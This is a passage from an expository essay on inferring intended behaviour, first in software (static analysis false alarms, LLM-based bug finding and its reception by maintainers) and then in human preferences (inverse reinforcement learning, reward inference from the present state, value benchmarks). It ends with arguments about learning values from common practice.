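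In one example, a comment says a function will "consume a quoted string". The word "consume" implies that the program should move past the text it has read. In one branch, the programmer had forgotten to move the reading position forward, although the function still returned the right text. SpecProbe's postcondition exposed the bug by requiring the position to be higher after the call than before it.

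The researchers tested SpecProbe on 726 past bugs in Java projects, using functions that developers had changed to fix them. A small model they trained for the task wrote ten postconditions for each function. For 80 bugs (11%), at least one postcondition held in the fixed version and failed in the buggy one. GPT-5.5 wrote at least one such postcondition for 233 bugs (32%).

In these tests, Zhang and colleagues told the model which functions to examine. To see how it did without that help, they had the small model write one postcondition for each of 500 randomly selected functions that the fixes hadn't changed. Of the 500 postconditions, 287 agreed with the code, 119 couldn't run and 94 disagreed with the code. The researchers read the 94 disagreements and found that 84 were the model's mistakes, usually because the postcondition was stricter than the description. In seven cases the description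 was ambiguous, and in only three did it clearly conflict with the code. The researchers therefore recommend SpecProbe for functions that a developer already suspects, and not for whole projects.

SpecProbe's results also depended on what people had written down. It did best on bugs that developers had fixed by adding a single statement to return a different result, revealing 14 of 37. It revealed none of the 39 bugs that involved reading or writing streams of data, where the rules are mostly unwritten. In one, a function that encodes text added a line break even when the text was empty. It should have returned nothing, but its documentation didn't mention that case.

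## Reports from working developers and deployed tools

The developers who maintain a program may know what it should do even when nobody has written the rule down. Companies that sell or use bug finders ask developers every day what their code should do. Developers are well placed to answer, but they are busy and sometimes mistaken, and they judge only the code that a tool reports.

### "I meant to do that"

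Coverity began selling the Stanford group's checker in 2002 and had about 700 customers by the end of 2009. Its staff ran the checker on a potential customer's code and showed the programmers the warnings within hours. Bessey and colleagues (2010), in *A Few Billion Lines of Code Later*, recall that some programmers defended real errors. One, whose program wrote past the end of a variable into the memory beside it, said, "No, I meant to do that; they are next to each other." Another wrongly insisted that the C standard lets a program write one place past the end of an array, and a heated argument changed nobody's mind.

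The first programmer intended the write, which makes it a deliberate exception. But the code worked only because the compiler had put the two variables side by side, and another compiler might not. The programmer would probably have wanted different code after thinking about this, so asking them established what they intended but not what they would want on reflection.

More often, programmers called a warning false because they didn't understand it. Bessey and colleagues found that a false-alarm rate above 30% easily caused problems. Users began to ignore the tool and missed the real errors among the false alarms. As they trusted it less, they dismissed more of the complicated real errors as false. Coverity aimed for a rate below 20% in its established checks. For years it also gave up looking for errors in which two tasks interfere with each other, like the lost addition to a shared counter,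 because they were harder to explain to users than to find.

The 30% limit on false alarms is a rule of thumb from one company's sales, not a measured threshold. Still, few of the tools that learn from common usage would have stayed under it. Even among MUDetect's highest-ranked reports, 78% were false alarms.

Some customers agreed that an error was real but did not fix it. Customers with more than about 1,000 reported errors usually recorded the old ones and fixed only new ones, since changing code that has run for years can break it. An odd line's survival in old code is therefore weak evidence that anyone wants it there.

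### Warnings that nobody acts on

For *Why Don't Software Developers Use Static Analysis Tools to Find Bugs?* (2013), Johnson, Song and colleagues interviewed 20 developers, 16 of them from one large company. Fourteen complained about the tools' output, including false alarms and the number of warnings. Nineteen said many tools didn't explain well enough what was wrong or what to do about it. All 20 thought the tools were worth using, but the researchers interviewed only people who had tried them.

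One participant wanted a way to record why he had dismissed a warning, for example because the code was safe now but might not be under certain conditions later. Such notes would also help anyone inferring intent, because they would mark deliberate exceptions that the code alone doesn't reveal.

Google calls a warning from its static analysis tools an *effective false positive* if the developer takes no positive action after seeing it (Sadowski et al., 2018, *Lessons from Building Static Analysis Tools at Google*). This includes warnings about real faults that the developer misunderstands and ignores, but not mistaken warnings that lead the developer to make the code clearer.

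Google gives an example involving a hash table, one kind of Java map. Its `contains` function searches the values, but programmers who call it often mean to search the keys. A warning about the call is useful even when the programmer did mean to search the values, because replacing it with `containsValue` makes the intention obvious to the next reader.

Google allows no effective false positives in checks that stop code from compiling, and up to 10% in checks that run during code review, when colleagues read a change before it is added to the shared code. One review check covered a function that inserts values into a message wherever the programmer has written `%s`. About once a week, a developer who had used a different marker complained that the warning was wrong, although it was right every time. The complaints stopped when the team reworded the warning to say that only `%s` works. This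 made the check more accurate by Google's measure, although it still detected the same mistake.

The choice of measure can greatly change the result. In May 2009, hundreds of Google engineers spent a week reviewing 3,954 FindBugs warnings. They filed bug reports for 44% but fixed only 16%. Sadowski and colleagues conclude that many warnings were correct but not important enough to act on.

In a Google survey, developers considered 74% of the problems flagged during compilation to be real, compared with 21% of those flagged in code already checked into the shared codebase. By then, testing and review had removed many of the serious errors.

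Companies count fixes partly because they can't measure recall. *Long Term Static Analysis Rule Quality Monitoring Using True Negatives*, a paper from Amazon, points out that a rule whose warnings developers often ignore may be raising false alarms or giving advice they can't act on. Sonar, which sells the checker SonarQube, reports a false-alarm rate of 3.2% among the 137 million issues on which users gave feedback in 2025, far below Coverity's target. But the figure is Sonar's own and leaves out issues that received no feedback. Much of what SonarQube checks is also general good practice, which doesn't require guessing what a particular programmer meant.

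### An Easter that isn't a Sunday

Language models have made it practical to infer a program's intended behaviour and test for it in live projects. Maaz, DeVoe and colleagues (2025), in *Agentic Property-Based Testing*, had an AI agent look for errors in 100 Python packages. Becker, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Just-in-Time Catching Test Generation at Meta*, tested changes Meta's engineers had just submitted. Help Net Security's *Most of the bugs Claude Mythos found have never been checked by a human* gives figures for a much larger search, in which Anthropic used its model Claude Mythos Preview to look for security flaws in 281 open-source projects.

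| Trial | Findings judged | Who judged them | Share accepted as real |
|---|---|---|---|
| Maaz and colleagues, random sample | 50 | Two of the researchers | 56% |
| Maaz and colleagues, top scores | 21 | The researchers | 86% |
| Becker and colleagues | 41 | Meta's engineers | 19.5% |
| Help Net Security, reviewed findings | 1,900 | Outside security firms | 90.8% |
| Help Net Security, reports sent | 1,596 | The projects' maintainers | 90.9% |

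Each percentage is the share of the findings selected for the judges to review that they accepted as errors. None of these percentages measures recall. They also come from different kinds of search, so they can't be used to rank the tools.

In *property-based testing*, a programmer states something that should be true for every input, and a computer tries many inputs to find one that breaks it. For example, splitting a dictionary into pieces and joining them again should give back the original. Maaz and colleagues' agent, which used Claude Opus 4.1, worked out such properties from documentation, comments and how other code used a function. It was instructed to test only properties that the code's developers claimed it had. It then wrote and ran the tests, and reconsidered each failure before reporting it. In a library for Amazon's cloud service, it found that the function for splitting dictionaries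 kept returning the first piece.

The agent wrote 984 reports. The researchers had Claude score them, then drew a random sample of 50 from the top 80%. The two graders at first agreed only moderately better than chance (a kappa of 0.31, where 0 is chance and 1 is complete agreement), and they settled their differences by discussion. They considered 28 of the 50 reports valid but only 16 worth sending to a maintainer.

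Maaz and colleagues estimate a cost of $9.93 per valid bug by applying the 56% to all the reports. This is a little optimistic, because the sample left out the lowest-scoring fifth. If none of those reports were valid, the cost would be about $12.40.

The researchers sent five reports to the packages' developers. Three led to accepted fixes, and a fourth had not yet been answered. The fifth concerned a function in python-dateutil that calculates the date of Easter. The agent assumed that Easter always falls on a Sunday and found years in which the function's date for the older Julian calendar did not. The maintainers replied that this was intended, since the function gives the date in the Julian calendar while Python works out the day of the week using the modern one. They agreed that this was confusing.

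Another report concerned `LookupDict`, part of the requests library. Its name and its place in the code suggest that it should behave like an ordinary Python dictionary, and the agent reported that it didn't. But the name was misleading. In a 2022 discussion of the same complaint, a maintainer had said that `LookupDict` was never meant to behave that way.

### Asking the engineer who made the change

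At Meta, Becker and colleagues looked for tests that passed on the old version of the code and failed on the new one. Such a test shows that a change altered the program's behaviour, but the engineer may have wanted that.

They generated these tests in two ways. The simpler method treated every change as a bug and wrote tests to expose it. The other had a model infer the purpose of the change from the code, title and summary, then list mistakes that someone pursuing that purpose might make. The model put those mistakes into the old code and wrote tests that would catch them. Inferring the purpose produced a failing test for 7.9% of changes, compared with 4.0% for the simpler method, but the comparison doesn't show how many of the failures were real errors.

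Most of the failing tests were false alarms, so the researchers used language models and handwritten rules to decide which ones deserved attention. One rule prioritised any change in behaviour when the engineer had described the code change as a refactoring, which reorganises code without changing what it does. In that case the description and the behaviour contradict each other, like conflicting MUST beliefs in Engler and colleagues' checkers.

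Between mid-September and the end of October 2025, Becker and colleagues messaged 41 engineers to ask whether a change in behaviour was intended. Eight confirmed an error, and the researchers judged that four of these errors would have caused serious failures. The messages described the change, for example that an expression that used to be true was now false, but left out the test. Engineers could usually answer within a few minutes. About 80% of the messages were false alarms, far more than Coverity's customers would accept, but each was so quick to dismiss that the researchers saw almost no effect on the engineers' work.

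The engineers had the change fresh in their minds, unlike someone explaining a line of code written five years ago. But saying that a change was intended is the quickest way to end the conversation, so a few of the other 33 changes may have contained errors that nobody looked into. The researchers also chose which findings to ask about, so precision across all the failing tests was probably much lower.

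### What reached the maintainers

The maintainers of curl, an open-source program for transferring data over the internet, used to pay for reports of security flaws. In 2025 many people sent them reports that a language model had written and nobody had verified. Daniel Stenberg, who leads the project, said that fewer than 5% of that year's reports were real, compared with more than 15% in earlier years. The project stopped paying for reports at the end of January 2026.

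In September 2025 Joshua Rogers sent curl a long list of possible errors that he had found with AI tools, and it led to about 50 fixes, so the use of AI alone wasn't the problem. In *Finding bugs across the Python ecosystem with Claude and property-based testing*, Maaz and colleagues also describe checking extensively by hand before they reported anything.

Newer models also do more of the checking themselves. Engineers at the database company Materialize compared two versions of Claude in a limited trial. According to their report, *Finding Bugs using LLMs*, the newer version found no more bugs but raised fewer false alarms, because it read more of the surrounding code to check that a bug could really occur. Missing context of this kind had caused most of CREED's false alarms.

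By May 2026 maintainers were receiving many credible reports. They had acknowledged 1,451 of the 1,596 reports they had received from the Mythos search, but only 97 fixes had gone into the projects, about 6% of the reports. Counting only fixes would make the reports look nearly worthless, though many fixes may have just taken longer.

Outside reviewers had not examined the other 21,119 of Mythos's 23,019 candidates, which Anthropic attributes to a shortage of reviewers. Anthropic (2026) counts every distinct crash or suspected flaw that Claude produces as a candidate, before anyone sorts them. If the outside firms started with the most promising candidates, their 90.8% figure is too high for the rest.

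### Proving what nearly everyone wants

Most of these disagreements were about the purpose of a particular program. But few maintainers would defend a program that crashes on ordinary input or writes to the wrong part of memory, so a tool can look for such failures without knowing what the program is for.

Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes a project with the company Theorem that relied on this kind of inference. Claude wrote proofs of security properties for 123 open-source libraries, work that used to take experts years. The libraries already had *fuzz tests*, which run a program on huge numbers of generated inputs to see whether it fails. The Russian news site OpenNET explains in *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) that the researchers automatically converted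 these tests into formal specifications. Claude then proved that the programs wouldn't fail on any input of up to 64 megabytes, including those the tests had never tried. It also found hundreds of bugs that fuzz testing had missed and prepared fixes for them.

EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports proofs that, within a model of one kind of processor and of Linux, the programs won't crash, misuse memory or fail an assertion. The first two properties are much the same for every program. Assertions can be particular to one program, but somebody had already written them down, so Claude didn't have to infer what the developers wanted.

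A program can have all these properties and still do the wrong job. A compression library that turned every file into an empty one could do so without ever crashing. To rule this out, a proof needs a statement of what the library should produce. Few programs have a specification as precise as the one for zlib, a compression method, which is published as the standard RFC 1950. OpenNET reports that Claude proved that the Linux kernel's version of zlib conforms to this standard.

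*The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) describes how an Anthropic engineer had Claude formally describe one of Anthropic's own code libraries, which led to 16 sets of bug fixes. Tolmach and Klaus accept that the bugs were real but deny that such an exercise shows the code to be correct. They argue that as proofs become easier to produce, the main difficulty is deciding what to prove. Tolmach and Klaus's company sells help with that decision, but their argument holds regardless, because a proof covers only the specification it starts from.

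Researchers are using language models to look for violations of rules that nobody has written down. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) compares four ways to do this and finds that the simplest methods worked best. These violations rarely cause the crashes that automatic tools detect, so someone who knows the program may have to confirm that it is meant to follow the inferred rule. Confirming a rule about the date of Easter, for example, required a reply from the maintainers.

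## Proofs and simulations on recovering preferences from what people leave behind

The maintainers of python-dateutil could explain what their Easter function was for. An AI system that tried to infer what people want from their homes, habits or software would often have nobody to ask, so researchers have studied how much one can learn from behaviour alone.

Their main technique is *inverse reinforcement learning*. In ordinary reinforcement learning, a programmer writes a *reward function*, which gives a number to each action in each situation, and a computer searches for the behaviour that earns the highest total. In inverse reinforcement learning, the computer starts with someone's behaviour and searches for a reward function that would explain it.

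### One choice, three explanations

Armstrong and Mindermann (2017), in *Occam's razor is insufficient to infer the preferences of irrational agents*, proved that behaviour alone can't settle what a person wants. They describe a person using two parts. The reward function R represents the person's wants, and the *planner* p is whatever turns those wants into actions, including skill, bias and error. Together they produce the person's *policy* π, which is what the person would do in every situation:

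π = p(R)

An observer can see only π and has to work out both p and R. Suppose Alice is crossing a room with a vase in her way. She can step round it or walk into it, and she steps round it. At least three pairs of planner and reward function explain this:

| Planner | Reward for stepping round | Reward for walking into it | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Perfect: picks the higher reward | 1 | 0 | Steps round |
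| Anti-rational: picks the lower reward | −1 | 0 | Steps round |
| Indifferent: steps round whatever the rewards are | 0 | 0 | Steps round |

In the first row Alice wants to keep the vase intact. In the second she would rather break it, but she always does the opposite of what she wants. In the third she has no preference and steps round it automatically.

Watching Alice for longer doesn't help, because the same three explanations work for any policy. An observer can always assume that she gets a reward of 1 for whatever she does and 0 for everything else, or reverse both the reward and the planner, or suppose that she ignores rewards. The ambiguity remains even in Armstrong and Mindermann's setup, where the observer already knows what the person would do in every possible situation. A planner that ignores rewards is compatible with every reward function, so behaviour doesn't rule any of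 them out.

This matters if a robot has to choose on Alice's behalf. If rewards range from −1 to 1, the wrong choice could reduce her reward by as much as 2. The robot could lower the worst expected loss to 1 by tossing a coin, but no strategy guarantees a smaller loss. Armstrong and Mindermann cite a general result that, whatever an AI system does, its loss under some reward function is at least half the largest possible loss.

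### Why the simplest explanation doesn't help

Most people would find the anti-rational Alice absurd. Scientists often reject far-fetched explanations when simpler ones fit the evidence equally well, a principle known as Occam's razor. Armstrong and Mindermann tested whether this principle works here, measuring an explanation's simplicity by the length of the shortest computer program that produces it.

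Any pair that explains Alice's policy must contain enough information to reproduce it, so the explanation can't be much shorter than a program for the policy. The three explanations in the table are close to this minimum because each adds only a line or two to the policy, such as "give 1 to whatever Alice does". A realistic explanation probably needs a lot more. For example, irrelevant numbers, such as the last digits of their social security numbers, can change how much people will pay for something. A realistic planner would have to include the size of this effect and the reason it seems stronger for chocolate than for wine.

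Armstrong and Mindermann proved that the unrealistic pairs are among the simplest if the programming language can express a few basic operations briefly. They only conjecture that the realistic pair is longer, and support this with evidence such as people's disagreements about what counts as rational. Their result about reversed rewards doesn't depend on the conjecture. Adding two minus signs turns a realistic account of Alice into one in which she wants the opposite and plans in the opposite way. The two accounts are about equally long, so simplicity can't be used to pick out the realistic one.

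Suppose Alice steps round the vase by day but walks into it at night. Her behaviour fits two different explanations. The obvious one is that she wants the vase intact but can't see in the dark. The other is that she plans perfectly and wants to break it at night. Calling the collision a mistake assumes something about what she wants, and a bug finder that labels a deviation a slip relies on the same kind of assumption about the programmer. Alice's behaviour shows only the combined effect of her planner and her wants, just as a count of deviations gives only the sum of s and d.

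### Assumptions about human error

Armstrong and Mindermann call the missing information *normative assumptions*, beliefs about what people are likely to want and what counts as roughly rational behaviour. People often agree about one another's wants and mistakes, so they must share some of these assumptions.

*Estimating cognitive biases with attention-aware inverse planning* (2025) describes how inverse reinforcement learning usually assumes that people act optimally apart from random noise. They may choose almost at random between similar options, but they rarely make a serious mistake. This assumption rules out the anti-rational Alice, but it fails in the dark room. If she walks into the vase every night, random noise is a poor explanation, so an observer using this method will wrongly conclude that she wants to. To avoid this error, the observer needs an assumption about how well she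 can see in the dark.

*Supervised Reward Inference* (2025) proposes collecting behaviour on tasks where researchers already know the reward. For example, they could pay people to cross a dark room without touching a vase and count the collisions. This would provide the kind of error rate that the count of locks lacked. Researchers would still have to assume that the participants wanted the money and that people are equally clumsy at home.

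People's errors can be informative when modelled well. *Mitigating Cognitive Bias in RLHF by Altering Rationality* (2026) cites 2021 work by Chan and colleagues in which modelling people's systematic irrationality improved the inferred rewards. However, *Learning the Preferences of a Learning Agent* (2026) points out that earlier methods of this kind assume a person's behaviour stays the same over time. A beginner's mistakes may disappear with practice even though their preferences haven't changed.

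It might also help to look at how someone reached a decision. In Armstrong and Mindermann's example, Alice is playing poker with Bob and stays in with a hand that loses only if he holds two particular tens. Perhaps she wants his money and has worked out that she will probably win. Or she may want to flatter him by losing, and take his confidence as a sign that he has the tens. If Alice were a computer program, its code might show whether it calculates the odds from the cards or from Bob's behaviour, and whether it stays in when it expects to win or when it expects to lose. But a reader would have to trust that a variable called `P_win` holds the chance of winning, and nobody has labelled the parts of a human brain. A program's source code also shows only how the program makes decisions, not how its programmer did.

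Someone else may also have influenced the behaviour. Armstrong and Mindermann describe a system that shows people manipulative advertisements and concludes from their purchases that they really like the products. An observer could instead treat the purchases as errors caused by the advertisements, but only after deciding that people didn't want the products.

### What an intact vase shows

Shah and colleagues accept the usual assumption of noisy rationality and ask what a robot could learn without watching anyone. Their method, Reward Learning by Simulating the Past (RLSP), uses only the state of a room when the robot arrives. It considers everything that Alice might have done beforehand and calculates how probable the present state s₀ would be if she had a given reward function R:

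P(s₀ | R) = the sum of P(past | R) over every possible past that ends in s₀

The probability of each past is the product of the probability of its starting state, the probability that someone with reward R would choose each action, and the probability that each action would have the result it did. RLSP then looks for the reward function that best explains the present state.

Suppose Alice has three equally short routes to a door, and one of them goes through a vase. If she doesn't care about the vase and picks a route at random, it has a 2/3 chance of surviving one crossing. If she cares enough never to take that route, it always survives. An intact vase after one crossing therefore gives a likelihood ratio of only 1.5 in favour of her caring. After ten crossings, a vase she didn't care about would have only a 1.7% chance of being intact, so the ratio rises to about 58. But if none of her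 routes goes near the vase, its survival is no evidence of what she wants.

The researchers tested RLSP without human participants in *gridworlds*, simulated rooms divided into squares. They chose what Alice wanted and gave the robot an instruction that left some of it out. A reward inferred from the present state tends to favour leaving everything as it is, so the robot added the inferred reward to the instructed one, and the researchers adjusted the balance between the two. They compared RLSP with three alternatives: following the instruction alone, penalising any change to the room, and penalising actions that put other states out of reach.

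| Test | Instruction alone | Penalise changes | Penalise lost options | RLSP |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Vase near Alice's route | Fails | Succeeds | Succeeds | Succeeds |
| Moving toy train | Fails | Fails | Succeeds | Succeeds |
| Apples in a basket | Fails | Fails | Fails | Succeeds |
| Batteries, full instruction | Succeeds | Partly succeeds | Partly succeeds | Succeeds |
| Batteries, incomplete instruction | Fails | Fails | Fails | Succeeds |
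| Vase far from Alice's route | Succeeds in no case | Succeeds | Succeeds | Fails |

In the second test, the robot that penalised changes stepped on the toy train to stop it from moving. In the third, the robot had no instructions, but RLSP inferred from two apples in a basket that Alice wanted apples picked. In the battery tests, one of two batteries was missing and the train was running. RLSP inferred that Alice wanted the train to run and also that she disliked batteries, because either preference would explain the missing battery. The mistake did no harm there, but it could cause harm in a house where someone was saving batteries for a torch.

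The robot using RLSP broke the distant vase when it knew where Alice had started, because she would never have gone near the vase from there. When it instead treated every starting position as equally likely, it considered routes on which she could have broken the vase, and it avoided the vase.

The robot also needs to know roughly how long Alice has been in the room. If it overestimates this, it still learns what not to break, because a vase that has survived longer is stronger evidence of care. But it underestimates how much she wants things done, because if it thinks she picked only two apples in 100 steps, it concludes that she can't have cared much about apples.

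These successes depend on strong assumptions. The robot was given an exact model of how its world worked and a handmade list of the features that might matter, such as the number of broken vases. It also assumed that Alice was nearly rational. If it had assumed that she acted against her own preferences, the same intact vase would have suggested that she wanted to break it. Shah and colleagues also mention preferences that people haven't acted to satisfy. For example, people want the air to contain oxygen, but RLSP wouldn't infer this preference because people didn't put the oxygen there.

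### Running the past backwards

Adding up every possible past is feasible only in tiny worlds. Lindner, Shah and colleagues (2021), in *Learning What To Do by Simulating the Past*, replaced the sum with neural networks that simulate likely pasts. Their method repeats three steps:

1. Starting from the present state, simulate backwards to estimate what the person did.
2. From the earlier state this reaches, simulate forwards as if the person had the reward function that the method currently guesses.
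3. Raise the reward for features that are more common in the backward simulation, and lower it for those that are more common in the forward one.

If the current guess is that Alice wants to break the vase, she breaks it in the forward simulation, but it stays intact in the backward one. The method therefore raises the reward for an intact vase.

Lindner and colleagues tested this on simulated jointed bodies. They trained a controller using the true reward, then gave their method a single moment from its performance. They also tried a simpler method that ignores the past and rewards the body for staying close to its state at that moment. The table gives average scores from three runs.

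| Task | Controller trained on the true reward | Full method | Staying similar |
|---|---|---|---|
| Balancing a pendulum | 1,000 | 303 | 6 |
| Cheetah running forwards | 13,236 | 4,591 | 6,466 |
| Cheetah running backwards | 13,361 | 5,730 | 12,443 |
| One-legged hopper, with a penalty for falling | 3,363 | 1,850 | 2,537 |

The simpler method did better on three of the four tasks. The data for each moment included the speed of the joints as well as their positions, so a single moment of running shows most of what the body is doing. The full method's lead on the pendulum is also less certain than it looks, because the method's standard error of 299 implies that one run scored about 900 and the other two almost nothing.

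Simulating the past helped more with unusual skills. From a single moment of a cheetah balancing on its front leg, the full method learned to balance and hop slowly forwards, though it sometimes fell over. The simpler method produced nothing similar. The joints were moving slowly at that moment, which suggested the cheetah was holding the position and not halfway through a flip. A single moment from a jump was less informative, and the method needed 50 moments to match the original jump closely.

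Preferences are harder to infer from real homes. Lindner and colleagues point out that if Bob has been too busy to tidy a room, the mess doesn't show how clean he would like it to be. Their method also assumes that one person produced the present state, but most places are the work of many people who limit what the others can do. If Alice likes fresh air and Bob feels the cold, a closed window may show only that Bob was the last to leave. Similarly, a line of code in shared software may survive because one programmer insisted on it.

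Later work on household robots infers more modest preferences. In *Personalized Robotic Object Rearrangement from Scene Context* (2025), a robot uses the current positions of a user's belongings, and earlier arrangements if it has seen any, to decide where to put new objects. This is especially difficult when the user would accept several places for the same object. Meng and Carreno-Medrano (2025), in *Explaining Why Things Go Where They Go*, separate four reasons for putting an object somewhere: it fits the space, it is easy to reach, it is near related things, or people would expect to find it there. A planner that used participants' preferences about these reasons produced arrangements close to the participants' own. Only the last reason is a corpus norm, and a cup in a kitchen cupboard could be there for any of the four.

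### What people infer from cookie crumbs

People often make such inferences, so researchers can compare their methods with human judgments. In *Social inferences from physical evidence via Bayesian event reconstruction*, Lopez-Brau, Kwon and Jara-Ettinger (2022) showed participants plans of a room with up to three doors, three possible goals in the corners, and a pile of cookie crumbs on the floor. Participants judged which goal someone had been heading for and, if there was more than one door, which door that person had used.

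The researchers' model resembles RLSP. For each door and goal, it assigns probabilities to the paths a person might take, with higher probabilities for efficient paths, and adds up the chances that the person would drop crumbs in that spot. It then compares the totals.

| Experiment | Participants | Correlation with the model |
|---|---|---|
| Infer the goal and the door | 40 | 0.94 |
| The same, with a record of nine earlier visits | 160 | 0.91 |
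| Judge whether one or two people had been there | 40 | 0.76 |

A simpler model that used mainly the distances from the crumbs to the doors and goals correlated at only 0.49 with judgements about the goal and 0.19 with judgements about the number of people. In another experiment, 40 participants drew the path they thought the person had taken. The doors and goals in these drawings correlated at 0.89 with the judgements in the first experiment. This supports the idea that people reconstruct what happened and don't just pick the nearest corner.

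A high correlation shows that people reason much as the model does, but it doesn't show that their inferences about other people are correct. Nobody had walked through these rooms, so the participants' answers couldn't be checked against a real person's goal. The researchers had also told them that the person went straight to one of three goals, which removed most of the uncertainty about how the person planned. Participants inferred only which corner someone walked to, which is much narrower than inferring what that person values.

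*Traces of Our Past*, a review by Jara-Ettinger and Schachner (2024), describes experiments in which people consider the reasons behind a design when judging whether it was copied. If two people build the same inefficient toy track, observers tend to suspect copying. They are less suspicious if the shared design is efficient, because both builders could have found it independently. The same reasoning could help show whether 20 programmers who wrote the same code had copied it, because an odd but harmless detail in all 20 programs would be a reason to suspect copying.

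### Values and the features that accompany them

Language models can infer preferences from a person's past choices without a handmade list of features, but it is unclear which aspect of the choices they will treat as important. *Deep Value Benchmark* (Ashkinaze, Shen and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a patient who keeps choosing doctors who take time to explain the treatment. All of them happen to be family doctors. An assistant could conclude that the patient values good explanations or that they want family doctors.

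The benchmark deliberately creates such coincidences. A model reads 5, 20 or 40 choices by an invented user who always prefers, say, an option that avoids harm and uses formal language to one that promotes justice and uses informal language. The model then has to predict the user's choice between an option that avoids harm but uses informal language and one that promotes justice but uses formal language. If it chooses the option that avoids harm, it has generalised the *deep value*, which Ashkinaze and colleagues describe as something people want to want on reflection. Otherwise it has generalised the *shallow preference* for formal language.

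Across 104,725 answers, nine models chose the deep value only 30% of the time, compared with 50% for random guessing. Every model did worse than chance, from 23% for GPT-4.1 mini to 40% for Gemini 2.0 Flash. Larger models did slightly worse than smaller ones overall. The models date from 2024 and early 2025, so newer ones may behave differently.

The 30% shows which explanation the models tend to assume when the evidence supports both, so it isn't straightforwardly an error rate. The value and the style predicted the user's earlier choices equally well, so nothing in those choices showed which one mattered. More examples didn't help, and the scores were almost the same with forty as with five. The models usually assumed that the user cared about style, and they could be right, since a user who always picks formal language may really care about it.

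When the researchers told the models to generalise the deep value, the average rose only to 33%, even though this removed the ambiguity about what to do. Asking the models to reason step by step lowered the average to 25%, and their reasoning often mentioned the surface features. But the models were good at matching values to the options when told which values were involved. People also did well, predicting the matching choice in 91% of 200 trials when told which value a user preferred. The models' main difficulty therefore seems to be working out which value a person was following in a series of choices.

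## Arguments for and against taking values from common practice

A few choices can fit two explanations equally well, as they did for the patient who kept choosing family doctors. The things people build contain far more choices, most of which required money or effort. Someone could therefore collect many artifacts, find the corpus norms and treat them as evidence of what people value. A deviation from those norms would then probably mean that the maker had failed to serve a shared value.

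Nobody seems to have published a proposal to look for values the way bug finders look for errors. GreaterWrong's *Value Learning*, an index of writing on how AI systems could learn human values, includes related ideas, such as learning a society's values from its laws. The case for and against the proposal therefore has to draw on evidence about software, legal work on custom, and alignment researchers' writing about values.

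### What artifacts add to answers and ratings

One argument for taking values from common practice is that asking people directly is less reliable. *Value Inference in Sociotechnical Systems* (Liscio, Lera-Leri and colleagues, 2023) argues that questionnaires often produce incomplete and hypothetical answers that don't match how people behave. Someone can tick a box marked "privacy" without sacrificing anything, whereas a company that deletes its customers' records after 30 days has paid programmers to set that up and given up data it could have used. Anyone who wanted to fake a norm of deleting records would have to persuade thousands of companies to do it.

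Artifacts also record trade-offs that people wouldn't think to mention. Few people would list the chance to undo a mistake among their values, but many programs ask for confirmation before permanently deleting a file, while few ask before moving one to another folder. The difference shows roughly how much interruption people will accept in return for protection.

Alignment researchers mostly use ratings instead. A person or another AI model compares two answers to the same prompt and picks the better one, and developers train the model to give more answers like it. *Toward a Theory of Value in AI Alignment* (Smart, Ahmed and colleagues, 2026) reviews 94 papers on value alignment from 2016 to 2024 and records the assumptions about values in each one, with two reviewers judging each paper.

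| Finding | Share of papers | How often reviewers agreed |
|---|---|---|
| Doesn't define or describe values | 79% | 75% |
| Uses preferences to stand for values | 82% | 86% |
| Treats values as measurable | 90% | 89% |
| Doesn't say whose values it means | 91% | 80% |
| Treats values as unchanging | 53% | 51% |

The reviewers agreed only slightly more often than chance about whether papers treated values as unchanging (a kappa of 0.13), so the figure for that question means little. The 82% is less surprising than it looks, because Smart and colleagues chose from papers that cited four influential works on learning from human preferences and feedback. The 91% matters most here, because an AI system can't follow human values without following some particular people's values, and hardly any of the papers named those people.

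Artifacts have a clear advantage over these ratings because a staircase or a payroll program had to work for somebody. According to Smart and colleagues, many rating datasets contain largely nonsensical conversations, in which raters pick the less absurd of two unrealistic answers. But the proposal shares the main assumption behind the ratings, that an observer can infer people's goals from what they do. Smart and colleagues trace this assumption to the economic theory of revealed preference. An observer also can't tell whose values a collection of artifacts records without knowing who built them and who had to live with them.

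### The conditions that bug finders rely on

Deviations from common practice are good evidence of bugs when many people worked independently, wanted the same thing, mostly knew how to achieve it, and can confirm what they meant. These conditions hold less often for values.

A theorem that the Marquis de Condorcet published in 1785 shows how much the reliability of a majority depends on people's independence and competence. Suppose 101 people each have a 60% chance of picking the better of two options. If they choose independently, the majority is right about 98% of the time. If each has only a 40% chance, the majority is right about 2% of the time, and adding more people lowers that further. Common influences can also make the majority less reliable. If each person has a 60% chance but their choices have a correlation of 0.1, the 101 people are equivalent to only about nine independent ones,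 whose majority is right about 73% of the time.

Buildings, like pasted code, are often not independent of each other. Ten thousand houses with stairs of the same height may reflect a single building regulation. That regulation may still be good evidence of what people need if its writers studied how people fall.

Purposes also vary more outside programming. Nearly every programmer whose code takes a lock wants it released eventually, but people who do similar things elsewhere may want different results. After Charlie Chaplin died, CBS showed clips from his films without paying for licences. Two US courts held this against CBS because the industry customarily licensed clips. Rothman (2013), in *Copyright, Custom, and Lessons from the Common Law*, points out that the industry didn't usually license clips for obituaries, although it often did for projects with more time. The courts had used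 the wrong comparison group, like a bug checker that flags functions meant to keep a lock. Even one person's priorities can change with the situation. Liscio and colleagues give the example of someone who generally puts freedom before safety but does the opposite in a pandemic.

Most programmers know how to release a lock, partly because a program that doesn't release one freezes and its users complain. Encryption mistakes produce no such feedback, and most apps broke basic encryption rules. The harm from a badly designed building or institution may take decades to appear, or may fall on people who cannot complain to its makers. Condorcet's theorem also assumes that one option really is better, but people with different values may disagree about which one.

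The last condition is that someone can confirm the inference. People are usually less sure about their values than an engineer is about a recent change to a program. Liscio and colleagues argue that values are often implicit in people's thinking, so behaviour may not reveal them, and that many people can express their values only in concrete situations. They conclude that computation alone can't infer values and people have to take part by reflecting on their values and discussing them with others.

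Their paper sets out a framework and doesn't test it. Its reasons show that inference from behaviour is likely to be poor, but not that it is impossible. Armstrong and Mindermann's proof about planners and rewards does show impossibility, but only for inference from behaviour alone. A computer could also read people's written justifications for their decisions. Liscio and colleagues recommend using these along with actions, much as a careful reader of code also reads the comments.

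### When a whole trade is wrong

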